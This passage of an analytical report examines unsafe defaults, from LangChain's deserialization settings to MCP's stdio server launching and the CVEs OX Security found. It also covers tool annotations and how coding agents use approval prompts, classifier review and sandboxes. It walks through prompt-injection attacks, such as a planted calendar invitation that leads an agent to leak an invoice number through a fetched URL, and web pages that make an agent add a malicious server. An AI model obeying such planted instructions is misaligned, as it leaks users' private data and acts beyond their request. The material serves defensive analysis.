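The name is much clearer than `weights_only=False` or `use_docker=False`, neither of which mentions a risk. Like Ruby's `unsafe_load`, it is also easy for a reviewer to find. It is unclear whether the word makes programmers less likely to accept the risk. A good test would show two groups of programmers the same error with different names for the setting, but no one seems to have published one. There is also no good count of how many tutorials include the argument, or how often models add it to code they write.

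The available evidence suggests that an alarming name does not stop people from using a feature they want. Most website security policies with a rule about scripts still allowed `'unsafe-eval'`, although many of those sites may have needed it, and more sites might have allowed it under a milder name. A name can also leave the danger unclear, as `trust_remote_code` did for many Hugging Face users.

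LangChain's setting broke document search for AWStaku, a user of the commercial data-analysis platform Dataiku. The error message warned that pickle files can run malicious code and told the user to set `allow_dangerous_deserialization` to `True` only for a trusted file. The call was in Dataiku's code, however, so the user could not change the setting. The reply on Dataiku's forum was to go back to the old default by installing an earlier version of the LangChain package, which loaded the file without requiring the setting, until Dataiku released a fix.

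LangChain's error message includes the name of the setting that turns the error off. A hurried programmer can copy it straight into the code, and a model asked to fix the error will presumably do the same. According to the message, this is safe in some cases, for instance when the programmer created the file and nobody else has changed it, which is probably true of most search indexes. But if the correct response is usually to type `True`, people may stop noticing the word "dangerous", much as Office users got used to pressing Enable Content.

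The advice to trust the source is harder to apply to `allow_dangerous_code` than to a particular file, because the setting permits every program the model will write, including those it writes after reading a stranger's text. Deciding whether to enable it would be easier if the code ran in a container, since the programmer would only have to consider what the container can reach.

LangChain has not used the word consistently. In 2024, a second function for loading search indexes still unpickled data without requiring the argument, until version 0.2.4 of the package (OSV's *PYSEC-2026-1514* (2026)). The word is also missing from `init_validator=None`, a setting LangChain added in December 2025 that lets `load` accept Jinja2 templates again, which can allow arbitrary Python to run.

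## The Model Context Protocol: launching local servers and labelling tools

In MCP, the command that starts a local server comes from a settings file, whereas the dangerous code in agent frameworks usually comes from a model. The user may have typed the command, but it can also come from an install button on a website, a stranger using a shared web service, or the agent itself. MCP's maintainers assume that whoever supplies the command is entitled to run programs on the machine that executes it. In April 2026 the security company OX Security published attacks on products where that assumption was false, and argued that MCP's official software development kits should restrict the commands they accept.

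### Running the command before checking it

An MCP client can connect to a server in two standard ways. It can send requests over the web to a remote server, which runs on another machine. It can also start a local server on its own machine and exchange messages with it through standard input and output, the text channels that every program has. Clients should support this second method, called stdio, "whenever possible", according to the November 2025 specification (Model Context Protocol, 2025).

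A typical settings entry for a local server contains this:

```
{"command": "python", "args": ["myapp.py"]}
```

The client uses it as follows:

1. It reads the command and its arguments.
2. It asks the operating system to run them as a new program, normally with the client's own permissions.
3. It sends the program an MCP message and waits for a valid reply.
4. If the reply is valid, the client can ask for the list of tools. Otherwise it reports an error.

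The client checks whether the program is an MCP server only at step 3, after the command has run. If the entry's command deletes files, the files are gone before the error appears. Java had a similar flaw, because it built an object before checking its type, but its maintainers could add an earlier check because the class name comes first in the stream. An MCP client can also read the command in advance, but it cannot tell from `python myapp.py` whether the script reports the weather or steals passwords. Cantina's *MCP stdio code execution risk* quotes the official Python SDK's code, which defines the command only as a string.

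### What OX Security found

OX's researchers started with GPT Researcher, an open-source program that lets users add their own MCP servers. They found that any system command entered there would run. ITPro's *AI agents using Anthropic MCP could be a vector for supply chain* quotes them: "The error was returned to the user; the command ran anyway." They first suspected a LangChain package that GPT Researcher used, but then traced the behaviour to Anthropic's original MCP code.

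OX Security's *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains* reports ten CVEs and successful attacks on six live platforms. Its list gives the same CVE number to two products. A later version of the company's findings, OX Security's *MCP Supply Chain Advisory*, corrects this and contains twelve CVEs. The products differ in who could choose the command:

| Product | Whose machine runs the command | Who could choose the command |
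|---|---|---|
| LangFlow, a tool for building AI workflows | The operator's | Anyone who could reach the server, without logging in |
| Letta, a platform for agents with long-term memory | Letta's | Any user with an account |
| Bisheng, another AI platform | The operator's | Anyone, because registration was open |
| Windsurf, an AI code editor | The user's | The author of a web page that the agent read |

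Letta's developers do not seem to have meant to offer local servers. Their web page let users add only remote ones, but the service behind it still accepted local ones. Letta has since fixed its own site. OX found more than 915 copies of LangFlow on the public internet. LangFlow's maintainers took from 11 January to 18 March 2026 to respond directly to OX.

OX also estimates that "up to" 200,000 instances are vulnerable, a figure that appeared in many headlines, but it reports only about 7,000 publicly accessible servers. The kits' 150 million downloads do not measure exposure, because a program that uses a kit is open to this attack only if an untrusted person can influence the command. OX benefits if the problem looks large, because it sells software that finds such mistakes and announced new detection features along with the research. Smimite, whose team audited its own MCP server after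 reading the findings, thought the technical problem was narrower than OX's headline suggested. The attacks on live platforms are still serious, even if the estimate is far too high.

### What Anthropic said, and what others said for it

According to Tom's Hardware's *Anthropic's Model Context Protocol has critical security flaw exposed*, Anthropic declined to change the protocol and called the behaviour "expected". By then Anthropic had donated MCP to the Linux Foundation's Agentic AI Foundation.

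In its longest direct statement, quoted by ITPro, Anthropic said the problem is not a valid vulnerability because it "requires explicit user permission for the file change". That describes a coding tool that asks its user before editing the MCP settings file, but not LangFlow or Letta, where a stranger supplied the command without the operator's approval. Reports often say that Anthropic also called stdio a secure default and made developers responsible for checking input, but that wording is OX Security's paraphrase.

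Other developers gave similar answers. flyingpenguin's *Ox Security Report* quotes LangChain as saying that application authors must check untrusted input. It also quotes the developers of FastMCP, another MCP library, as saying that stdio starts a program "by design". SnakeYAML's maintainers had defended their loader in much the same way.

According to the Model Context Protocol project's security policy, a malicious local server "already has arbitrary code execution by virtue of being run". Starting a server therefore means trusting it, and the policy warns that stdio "is not a sandbox". The maintainers still accept reports of attacks that escape a sandbox or reach the software development kits' code through a remote connection. The policy covers attacks between a client and a server after one has started the other, but it doesn't address who should be allowed to choose the server.

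Accounts of when the guidance changed are confusing because they concern two different changes. ITPro reports that Anthropic updated its security policy after replying to OX, while flyingpenguin places the update after OX's "initial report". Both are referring to a note that people should use MCP adapters, especially stdio ones, with caution. The two accounts are compatible, but neither gives an exact date. The more important rules, on consent, go back to a July 2025 proposal, Model Context Protocol's *MCP Client Security Requirements for Local Server*, nine months before OX published its findings. The proposal warned that attackers could use one-click installation to run arbitrary commands.

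### The desktop user and the web service

The maintainers have the better argument when people run MCP clients on their own computers. Someone who writes `python myapp.py` in a settings file could type the same line into a terminal, so the client gives them no new power. Restricting the command would also make it harder for them to run servers they wrote.

This argument assumes that the user chose the command. With an install button, the website chooses it and the user only approves it. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* therefore requires a client with such a button to show the whole command, describe it as potentially dangerous and wait for approval. This warning is more informative than Office's old macro bar, which did not show what a macro would do. But many users cannot judge an unfamiliar command, and people who see too many prompts tend to stop reading them. *Security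 Best Practices* also recommends, but does not require, running local servers in a sandbox with few permissions.

The assumption fails completely for Windsurf. A web page could use prompt injection to make the agent add a server to the settings file, and Windsurf then started that server without asking the user. According to OX Security, Claude Code, Cursor, Gemini CLI and GitHub Copilot ask for at least one approval before such an edit, so their makers do not count it as a vulnerability. OX objects that users may approve the edit without knowing what it contains.

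OX is right about web services that accept settings from strangers. The stranger chooses a command that runs on the operator's machine, possibly beside other customers' data. The operator has not decided to trust the program and may not know that it is running. Some vendors told OX that they run the commands in a sandbox, such as a Docker container. OX agrees that this can protect other customers' data, but says an attacker could still use the machine for free, for example to mine cryptocurrency.

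The service's developers are still best placed to prevent this. A software kit receives the command as text, with no indication of whether the developer or a stranger wrote it. But the same was true of Ruby's YAML loader, and Patterson changed its default because too many applications were making the same mistake. OX's dozen CVEs suggest that a similar change is worth considering for MCP, if someone can find a default that helps web services without hindering desktop users.

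### Would OX's fixes work?

One of the changes OX has suggested to the official kits is an allowlist of commands. Flowise, another tool for building AI workflows, and the agent framework Upsonic already had allowlists, which permitted programs such as `python` and `npx` that many local servers need. But `npx` can also run a command passed to it as an argument, and OX used this to bypass both lists. Any list that permits an interpreter has the same weakness, but removing interpreters would exclude most of the servers people want to run.

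Another proposal is a named unsafe opt-in. OX Security's *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains*, the technical companion to the main report, gives this example:

```
StdioServerParameters(command="python", args=["myapp.py"],
                      allow_unsafe_command_execution=True)
```

The command here is the same as in OX's example of correct use. If even this call needs the setting, every program that starts a local server will contain the word "unsafe", and reviewers won't be able to tell dangerous calls from ordinary ones. LangChain's `allow_dangerous_deserialization` has a similar problem.

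A more promising idea is for developers to write the permitted commands, complete with their arguments, into their own program. Users would then choose from the list:

| The user sends | The service runs |
|---|---|
| `weather` | `python weather_server.py` |
| `calendar` | `python calendar_server.py` |
| Anything else | Nothing |

A stranger can then pick only from commands that the developer has approved. OX's remaining proposal, "manifest-only execution", would presumably do something similar by allowing only servers described in a fixed file. Developers can already write such a list, but a kit that required one would also protect those who had not thought about the danger. That requirement would probably have stopped the attack on Letta, whose developers would have had no reason to list any local servers. A desktop client would need an exception, since its users must be able to add their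 own servers.

Each project built on the kits would have to adopt the new version to benefit from a change, though OX says the change would protect them all "instantly". Some projects would switch the restriction off to keep existing features working, as several machine-learning libraries did with PyTorch's safe loader.

### Four labels with cautious defaults

Once a server is running, the client has to decide which of its tools the model can call without asking the user. Since March 2025, servers have been able to help by attaching labels, called annotations, to their tools. A post on the Model Context Protocol project's blog describes the four that concern a tool's behaviour:

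| Label | What it tells the client | If the label is missing | What a client might do with it |
|---|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | Whether the tool leaves everything unchanged | Assume it makes changes | Skip the approval prompt for a read-only tool |
| `destructiveHint` | Whether its changes can destroy something | Assume they can | Show a warning |
| `idempotentHint` | Whether repeating the same call is safe | Assume it is not | Retry a safe call after a failure |
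| `openWorldHint` | Whether the tool deals with outside people or systems | Assume it does | Check its output for untrusted content |

These defaults are the reverse of those in `pickle.loads` or the old `yaml.load`. If a developer adds no labels, the tool gets the most suspicious treatment. However, the protocol cannot make clients apply these defaults, and the server's author writes the labels.

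A malicious server can label a tool read-only and then delete the user's files when the model calls it. Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, raised this problem when the maintainers discussed the labels, asking how a client could use information it could not trust. Another participant, Basil Hosmer, wanted clients to ignore all labels from untrusted servers. The maintainers compromised by calling every label a "hint" and requiring clients to treat hints as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. Each client's developers decide how much weight to give the hints.

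Office had a better source of information about macros than an agent has about tools. The Mark of the Web comes from Windows, not from the document's author, so an attacker could not simply write a document that claimed to be local. A tool's labels come from whoever wrote the server, so an attacker can label a harmful tool as safe. The labels are still useful when the user already trusts the server's author. For instance, a company that runs its own servers can use the labels to let employees' agents read records freely but ask before deleting any.

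Clients apply the cautious defaults unevenly. The labels are optional and many servers have none, so a client that followed the defaults strictly would treat every tool on those servers as potentially destructive. If it asked for approval each time, it would prompt users even for a harmless search. Most clients instead trust any server the user has chosen to install. According to the Model Context Protocol blog, developers of autonomous agents tend to see approval prompts as friction and rely on sandboxes, while large companies want more labels than the protocol offers. At the time of the post, no client showed the labels in its approval prompts or let users filter tools by them.

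The closest equivalent in use was GitHub's read-only mode, which about 17% of users had turned on. Many of the other 83% presumably want their agents to make changes on GitHub, so we can't assume they all overlooked the setting. Still, this opt-in protection covers only a minority of users, as with browser policies against `eval`.

### Harmless tools in a dangerous combination

Even accurate labels can miss a danger that comes from using several tools together. The programmer Simon Willison uses the term "lethal trifecta" for the combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally. An attacker who controls some of the content an agent reads can try to make it send out the private data.

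Suppose a user asks an agent to plan the day, and the agent has these three tools:

| Tool | Correct value of `readOnlyHint` | What it adds |
|---|---|---|
| `read_calendar` | True | Untrusted content, because a stranger can send an invitation with instructions in it |
| `search_emails` | True | Private data |
| `fetch_page` | True | Outside communication, because the web address it requests can contain text |

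The agent reads an invitation containing instructions to find the latest invoice and open a web address ending in the invoice number. If the model follows them, it searches the email and requests the page, and the attacker reads the number in the web server's log. None of the tools changes anything, so a client that skips prompts for read-only tools would not ask the user for approval. Removing any one of the tools would prevent this attack.

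The combination resembles a gadget chain. Its parts can come from servers a user connected for different tasks, and no server's author can know what else is connected.

Researchers have demonstrated an attack of this type using a malicious calendar event, an MCP calendar server and a tool that runs code. The code tool mattered most, because an agent that can run any system command can read files and send them out without any other tool. The danger is the same if the code tool is built into the client instead of coming from an MCP server.

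A client could defend against such attacks by marking the session as tainted once the agent has read something from an outsider, then either blocking tools that could send data out or asking before each use. `openWorldHint` helps a little, because a server can use it to mark `fetch_page` as reaching the outside world. But none of the four labels identifies private data, so the client could not tell whether the agent had any.

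Several proposals would add the missing information, including one from GitHub and OpenAI on trust and sensitivity. A group of MCP contributors is now considering six of them, according to the Model Context Protocol project's page on the group's work, but the group can only make recommendations. By November 2026, the project's index listed no new labels among the accepted proposals. Jonathan Hefner, a maintainer, had asked what a client would do differently with the extra labels in an early draft. The blog post recommends network controls or a sandbox, rather than labels, to guarantee that a tool cannot send data out.

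### A timetable for removing features

The July 2026 revision gave MCP a formal policy for retiring features. Delimarsky, who wrote it, wanted a timetable that developers could plan around. The protocol's *Feature Lifecycle* classifies each feature as active, deprecated or removed. Anyone proposing to deprecate a feature must give a reason and explain what users should do instead. At least twelve months must pass between the release that first marks a feature as deprecated and its removal. The main software development kits must mark the feature as deprecated in their code and should print a warning when a program uses it.

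The ninety-day exception for urgent security problems applies only if someone has published an advisory or documented real attacks, and if there is no way to reduce the danger while keeping the feature. Stdio would probably not qualify despite OX's CVEs, because clients can ask for consent and operators can use a sandbox.

The maintainers applied the policy immediately to three features:

| Feature | What it does | Suggested replacement |
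|---|---|---|
| Sampling | Lets a server ask the client's model to write something | The server contacts a model provider directly |
| Roots | Lets a client tell a server which folders to work in | The client passes the folders to a tool, or the user puts them in the server's settings |
| Logging | Lets a server send its log messages to the client | The server writes to its error output or uses OpenTelemetry, a standard monitoring system |

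All three features still work. Their twelve months end on 28 July 2027, but the maintainers remove features only when they release a new specification. The Model Context Protocol roadmap sets the next release for 30 March 2027, which is too early to remove them, and another for September 2027. They will therefore last at least thirteen months, and probably longer, since removing any of them also requires a separate proposal.

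The timetable is less clear for HTTP+SSE, an older way of connecting to remote servers. The Model Context Protocol release announcement promises HTTP+SSE users a year to move, but the project's official list of deprecated features (Model Context Protocol, 2026) allows its removal three months after the policy became final. The list is authoritative under the policy, so developers who planned around the announcement could have less time than they expect. The maintainers have not yet removed any feature under the policy.

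The maintainers did make one large change without a deprecation period. The Model Context Protocol changelog records that the same revision removed the handshake that opened every connection and the sessions that followed it. They said the redesign needed a clean break, but that they did not intend such breaks to become normal. To ease the transition, they let updated clients fall back to the old handshake when connecting to an older server.

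### References that clients must not follow

The revision also introduced a safe default along with a new capability. An MCP tool describes its arguments in JSON Schema, a standard way of specifying what a piece of JSON should contain. Tool descriptions can now use the full standard, including references to definitions stored elsewhere:

```
{"type": "object",
 "properties": {"city": {"$ref": "https://example.com/city.json"}}}
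```

A client that followed this reference automatically would contact `example.com` as soon as it processed the tool's description, before the model had called any tool. A malicious server could replace the address with one inside a company's private network, which the client can reach but the attacker cannot. The release candidate notes (Model Context Protocol, 2026) say that implementations "must not auto-dereference" such addresses. The final changelog keeps requirements on references and adds limits on the resources a complicated description can use, because such a description could exhaust them, as YAML aliases can.

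This rule was probably easy to introduce because few programs could have relied on the behaviour it forbids. Changing stdio would be harder because every existing local server depends on the client running a command.

Other parts of the revision leave more work to developers. Now that the protocol has no sessions, a server that needs to remember something, such as a shopping basket, gives the model an identifier to send back with later calls. The server has to check each time that the basket belongs to the person asking, or anyone who learns the identifier could open it. Kale (2026) argues in *MCP's new spec turns a planted prompt into a stolen credential* that the revision shifts security enforcement from the protocol to developers in this way. That describes the identifiers reasonably well, although attackers could also misuse the old session numbers if a server did not check them properly.

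The changes to stdio concern how the client and server communicate after the client has started the server. Under the final stdio rules (Model Context Protocol, 2026), a local server can no longer initiate requests to the client. If it needs more information from the user, it must include that request in its reply to a client request. This should prevent prompts that appear without a clear reason, but a malicious program can still do damage without sending any MCP messages.

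A later change means that the command for launching a local server can run twice. Model Context Protocol's *Supporting protocol revision 2026-07-28* says that when a client checks which version a local server supports, the official TypeScript kit starts a second, short-lived copy of the server from the same settings. The latest draft of the specification still defines stdio as a program that the client launches. None of the proposals in the November index would restrict which command the client runs, though the protocol's security group lists the isolation of local servers as a matter for the transports group.

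## Approval prompts and sandboxes in coding agents

A coding agent works on a programmer's own files. To fix a failing test, it might read a dozen of them, edit two, install a package and run the tests again. Each product's developers decide which of these actions need the user's permission. Until August 2026, Anthropic's Claude Code asked before almost every edit and command. Now a second model checks most of the risky actions instead. Anthropic's announcement, *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), argues that users approve nearly every prompt, often by reflex, so the prompts protect them less than they seem to.

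### What runs before the user changes any settings

Anthropic's *Permission modes* describes Claude Code's defaults in November 2026, and OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes those of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, in June. If a user starts each one in a project folder and changes nothing, this is what happens:

| Action | Claude Code before the change (Manual mode) | Claude Code now (auto mode) | Codex |
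|---|---|---|---|
| Read a file in the project | Runs | Runs | Runs |
| Edit a file in the project | Asks | Runs | Runs |
| Run the project's tests | Asks | A second model decides | Runs in a sandbox |
| Download a package the project lists | Asks | The second model normally allows it | Asks, because network access is off |
| Upload private code to a public site | Asks | The second model normally blocks it | Asks, for the same reason |
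| Setting that switches the checks off | `--dangerously-skip-permissions` | The same | `--dangerously-bypass-approvals-and-sandbox`, or `--yolo` |

Codex can run commands without asking because the operating system stops them from writing outside the project or using the network. It asks only when a command needs to go beyond those limits.

Both products give extra protection to files that control the agent. Codex cannot write to its own settings folder in the project. In Claude Code's auto mode, the second model reviews changes to such files, including the one that lists MCP servers. Claude Code also ignores instructions in a project's own settings file to switch the checks off, so a stranger cannot disable them for people who download the project.

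The settings that switch off the checks have alarming names, like LangChain's, but Codex also has the alias `--yolo` ("you only live once"), which is quicker to type and contains no warning. With its ordinary checks off, Claude Code still prompts the user before a few actions, such as running a command that would delete the user's home directory. Users can remove that prompt too, with the setting `CLAUDE_CODE_EVEN_MORE_DANGEROUSLY_SKIP_PERMISSIONS`. By Anthropic's count, a quarter of interactive sessions were already starting with the ordinary checks off.

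Zhong, Liao and colleagues (2026), in *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, compared the protections in six coding agents, including these three:

| | Gemini CLI | GitHub Copilot in VS Code | Cursor |
|---|---|---|---|
| Editing files in the project | Asks | Asks | Allows |
| Files outside the project | Refuses | Refuses | Allows |
| Built-in rules for shell commands | 75 | 122 | None |
| Sandbox for shell commands | Optional | Optional | On, but the user can rerun a failed command outside it |

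The first two rows apply only to the agent's built-in file tools. A shell command can access the same files without those tools, so the products also check each command's text against a list of rules. The comparison is out of date for Claude Code, which it shows asking before every edit, so its entries for the other products may be out of date too.

Personal agents, which act on a user's email and other accounts, are less consistent, sometimes even within a single product. For *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) tried five commercial agents in May and June 2026. In its ordinary chat mode, ChatGPT asked before every action that a permission setting covered, and they found no way to approve actions in advance. In agent mode, where ChatGPT operates a web browser on a remote machine, they could not set any permissions for the browser.

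### A survey that dated quickly

*Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem* (Wang, Li and Tian, 2026) examined 21 widely used agent products as of April 2026. In 16 of them, users could limit the agent's scope, for example to certain folders. Fifteen prompted for approval while the agent worked, and 14 accepted written rules. Defaults also differed. The coding agent Aider is open by default, with no sandbox, while Codex is closed by default and runs in a container without network access. Wang and colleagues consider open defaults convenient but prone to accidents, and closed ones safe but likely to get in the user's way.

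They found no product that relied on a model to judge whether an action matched the user's intent, and took this as evidence that companies had learned from experience to keep people involved. But Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* (2026) had already announced a preview of model-based approval on 24 March, and OpenAI described a similar feature for Codex on 30 April. Their count of zero may depend on how they defined reliance on a model, since auto mode also applies the user's own rules and sometimes goes back to asking the user for approval. Even so, a model now reviews actions by default in one of the leading products, so industry practice no longer supports their conclusion as it seemed to in April.

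### How people answer the prompts

Anthropic reports that Claude Code's users approve 97% of permission prompts. Even someone who read every prompt carefully might approve nearly as many, because most of the commands are probably safe. When Claude shows users a plan for the whole task, they reject 39% of the plans. This suggests that people use judgement when the question is worth their time, though a plan also gives them more to disagree with.

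Anthropic's better evidence comes from an experiment with 1,053 paid software testers. While each tester worked with the agent in a test environment, the researchers replaced the text of one approval prompt with a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused it 13.6% of the time. Auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands, including 800 that a tester had approved, and allowed only six that a tester had refused.

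The testers had little reason to worry, since neither the project nor the machine was theirs, and people may be more careful with their own files. But the testers refused fewer dangerous commands as the session went on, from about 17% early on to about 5% after fifty or more prompts. The artificial setting does not easily explain that decline, because it was the same throughout. Approval fatigue would produce such a decline, because users learn from each harmless prompt that the next one is probably harmless too, as happened with Office's Enable Content button.

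Programmers describe much the same thing. For *Let the Agent Do It?* (October 2026), Salerno, Gao and colleagues interviewed 18 software practitioners and then surveyed 115, of whom 107 answered the questions about permissions. Of those 107, 47.7% said they read requests carefully, 33.6% said they skimmed them, and 20.6% said they approved by default. A third said they had become less careful over time. One interviewee said that reading every request "really is exhausting", and another said that having to click every ten seconds defeated the purpose of a faster tool.

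About three-quarters of the respondents looked more closely at requests to write, delete or gain extra privileges, and 82.2% were readier to approve requests in an isolated environment. More than 60% said they would never grant access to sensitive data. Yet Claude Code's auto mode normally lets the agent read a project's `.env` file, where programmers often keep passwords and access keys. Some of the respondents who would refuse such access are presumably using a product that allows it without an approval prompt.

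Salerno and colleagues recruited people through their own contacts and social media, and people tend to overstate their diligence. People who review code carefully also don't always review an agent's actions carefully. CodeReport Global's *AI Coding Agent Permissions* (2026) describes a separate survey of 203 coding agent users. Among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the generated code, 61% often approved some kind of action without a close look.

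### Would people do better with rules of their own?

Users could decide in advance what an agent may do, instead of answering prompts one at a time. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, tested this with 113 people from outside the software industry. Each supervised an agent through the same simulated day of 18 actions, mostly email, travel and shopping. The day's tasks required 11 of the actions, and the other seven were overreach, such as buying a $25 airport lounge pass nobody had requested.

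One group of participants approved or refused every action themselves. In the second group, a model approved some actions and referred the rest to the participant. The third group wrote four rules before the day began, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting things and reading private data.

| | Person decides each time | Model reviews first | Person writes rules |
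|---|---|---|---|
| Participants | 34 | 44 | 35 |
| Prompts per person | 18 | 10 | 10.9 |
| Average time spent on permissions | 142 seconds | 120 seconds | 129 seconds |
| Overreach blocked | 59.6% | 53.9% | 39.6% |

The people who wrote rules blocked the least overreach. After statistical adjustment, they blocked about 20 percentage points less than those who decided each time. They also blocked about 14 points less than the group with a model, but that difference was not reliable once Yan corrected for multiple comparisons. The time they saved compared with those who decided each time was not reliable either.

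The participants who wrote rules chose "ask" for 114 of the 140, so the agent still prompted them during the day, and they usually said yes. They approved two-thirds of the overreach they saw, compared with 40% in the group that decided every time. Selection explains some of this difference, since anyone who had chosen "never" did not see those prompts and could not refuse them. But selection can't explain why the group that wrote rules blocked less overreach in total than the other group. Perhaps people who had just written rules assumed that the rules were already protecting them.

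In the group with automated review, the model referred all seven overreach actions to the participants, who approved them 46% of the time. If the model had refused everything it referred, it would have stopped all the overreach, but also three actions that the tasks required. Anthropic's classifier can refuse actions itself, so Yan's results for this group do not show how well auto mode would work.

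An overreach action is also not necessarily harmful. Of the 34 people who decided every time, 30 let the agent telephone the airport to confirm a flight, and many of them may have found the call useful. After recruiting people at random for all three groups, Yan added more participants only to the group that wrote rules, which makes the comparison less reliable.

Yan's participants refused most of the actions that went beyond the task, whereas Anthropic's testers missed most of the dangerous commands. The conditions were very different. Yan's participants read plain descriptions, and more than a third of the actions went beyond the task. The testers had to spot one dangerous command among many routine ones. Approval prompts probably work better when they are rare, easy to understand and often worth refusing.

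### Permissions that only get wider

Many products let a user answer a prompt with "always allow" or an equivalent, and the permission outlasts the task that prompted it. Wang and colleagues call this scope creep. They found only two products with any way to narrow an agent's scope again: Cursor, through its administrator settings, and OpenClaw. They also cite a July 2025 incident in which the coding agent Replit deleted a production database after a configuration meant for development had given it write access to live data.

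Anthropic reports that by June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule allowing some shell commands to run without a prompt. It says 5% allowed any shell command and another 43% allowed an interpreter such as Python. As with Flowise's allowlist, permitting an interpreter is hardly narrower than permitting every command. The share of users with such rules was growing by about five percentage points every five weeks.

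Auto mode partly reverses this. While it is on, Claude Code ignores rules broad enough to let the agent run arbitrary code, and the classifier checks the commands those rules would have allowed. Narrower rules, such as permission to run one project's tests, still apply. But the broad rules remain in the settings file and take effect again when the user leaves auto mode.

Salerno and colleagues recommend that tools not treat repeated approvals as a lasting preference, because the user may only be tired. Approvals that expire at the end of a task would fit this advice, but they would bring back some of the prompts that made people choose "always allow".

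### A second model answers the prompt

In auto mode, Claude Code handles most actions like this:

1. It applies any rules the user has written, for example to refuse a certain command.
2. If no rule decides the matter, it lets the agent read files and edit those in the project, apart from protected ones.
3. It sends nearly everything else to the classifier, a separate model that compares the action with the user's messages and a long list of things to block.
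4. If the classifier refuses, the agent learns why and looks for another way. After three refusals in a row, or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user.

The classifier does not receive the web pages and files that the agent has read, so text planted there cannot influence it directly. If the classifier returns no decision, Claude Code blocks the action. The classifier will also enforce an instruction the user gives during the conversation, such as "don't push", but shortening a long conversation may remove that instruction. Anthropic recommends a written rule for anything that needs a guarantee.

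OpenAI's version is narrower, because Codex's sandbox first limits what a command can reach and a reviewing model handles only requests to go beyond those limits. OpenAI's *Auto-review* calls this "a reviewer swap, not a permission grant". In the June documentation, these requests still go to the user by default. OpenAI's *Running Codex safely* says the company uses the reviewing model for its own staff and restricts network access to expected destinations.

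Anthropic has published other results in favour of auto mode. It re-examined real sessions that its safety systems had flagged and found serious harm that the user had not explicitly asked for in 6.3% of those with manual approval, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. But users chose their own mode, and those who kept manual approval may have been doing riskier work. Apollo Research, an AI safety company, also tested the classifier with artificial attacks. The classifier's miss rate fell from 12% to 7% after Anthropic strengthened it.

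A third test compared products. Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to run 72 prompt-injection scenarios ten times each:

| Models | Share of attacks that succeeded with a model reviewing actions | Share that succeeded without one |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic's latest models in Claude Code | 0% | 0.09% on average |
| GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex | 5.83% | 19.03% |

The test shows very little about what auto mode adds, because Anthropic's models resisted nearly all the attacks without it. The Codex row is better evidence that a reviewing model helps, since the attacks' success rate fell by more than two-thirds. Neither row covers the protections built into the companies' own browser extensions, because Trajectory Labs used its own browser connection.

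Anthropic benefits when users let Claude work unattended for longer, and it published all these figures to justify a change it had already decided to make. It also doesn't say how often auto mode blocked harmless commands in the experiment with testers. That rate matters because a classifier could catch every dangerous command by refusing everything, which would make it useless. The refusals do seem tolerable in practice, since only about 10% of sessions at Gusto, a payroll company that uses auto mode, include at least one.

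Wang and colleagues raise two objections that better test scores would not fully resolve. The first is that an attacker who can manipulate the agent may also be able to manipulate the model that guards it. Hiding web pages from the classifier reduces this risk, but a page can still influence which actions the agent requests. The second is that the model lacks information the user never gave, such as which of two databases is live. Any reviewer other than the user has the same problem, and the user's knowledge doesn't help if they approve a command without reading it.

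### Removing the question with a sandbox

A sandbox avoids many of these questions by limiting what a command can do. If a command cannot act outside the project or use the network, neither a person nor a model has to predict exactly what it will do. Without network access, a command also cannot send private data to an attacker, which removes one part of Willison's lethal trifecta.

OpenAI reported in April 2026 that, of 10,000 actions by Codex, 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox. The other 720 needed approval, and the reviewing model approved about 99% of them and refused roughly seven. In OpenAI's internal use, Codex found an acceptable alternative after more than half of refusals. Codex would therefore stop three or four times, which fits OpenAI's figure of about 200 times fewer stops. Most of the reduction in questions thus comes from the sandbox, before the model reviews anything. The reduction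 would be smaller compared with Claude Code's Manual mode, which already lets the agent read project files freely.

The sandbox's limits have to match what the work requires. OpenAI advises users who see too many approval requests to "fix the boundary first", for example by adding a folder, instead of relying on the reviewer to keep approving them. It also warns against broad rules, such as one that permits every Python command.

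People turn off sandboxes that fit their work poorly. Zhong and colleagues collected 290 public reports of coding agents misusing files, published between February 2024 and March 2026. In 41 of them, a sandbox had either blocked legitimate work or left something valuable exposed inside it. Several products respond to a blocked command by offering to run it again without the sandbox, and repeated offers push users to disable it altogether. We can't estimate from these reports how often sandboxes fail, because nobody files a report when a sandbox works.

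An agent that can edit a project inside a sandbox can still ruin it. In 40% of the cases of harm or demonstrated attack with a clear outcome, nobody could fully recover the losses. Zhong and colleagues built a file system called YoloFS that keeps the agent's changes separate until the user accepts them. In eight of 11 test tasks with hidden destructive side effects, the agent noticed and undid the damage. In the other three, the user could still reject the changes. On 112 routine tasks, YoloFS interrupted users less than the usual approval prompts did, with the same success rate.

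Neither method works as well for a personal agent, whose tasks often consist of changing something outside the machine. A file system such as YoloFS can hold back an edit but can't recall a sent email. In Yan's simulated day, the user's tasks required some spending, some sending and some deleting, but other actions of each kind went beyond those tasks. A sandbox that blocked all payments would have stopped the agent from buying the lounge pass, but also from booking the airport ride the user had asked for.

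## What the cases share and where they differ

Most of the functions in the earlier sections now have a safer default. AutoGen's developers made the change in four months, while Microsoft took about 21 years to make it for BinaryFormatter. Java's serializer still accepts any class after 29 years. Comparing the dates across the nine cases can rule out some simple explanations for why such a change is quick or slow, but nine cases are too few to prove one.

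### The timetable

This section dates each safe default from the first release in which a plain call stopped running code from its input. For PyYAML, that is version 6.0, where a call without a named loader fails. Version 5.1 doesn't count because its FullLoader turned out to be unsafe. For BinaryFormatter, it is .NET 8, which extended the block on using BinaryFormatter to simple console programs, according to Microsoft's *BinaryFormatter disabled across most project types*.

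| | First release | Safe alternative | First warning | Safe default | Unsafe behaviour removed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Office macros from the internet | By 1995 | 2016, as a setting for administrators | After 1995; the Enable Content bar in 2010 | July 2022 | No |
| Java serialization | 1997 | 2017, as an optional filter | None | None yet | No |
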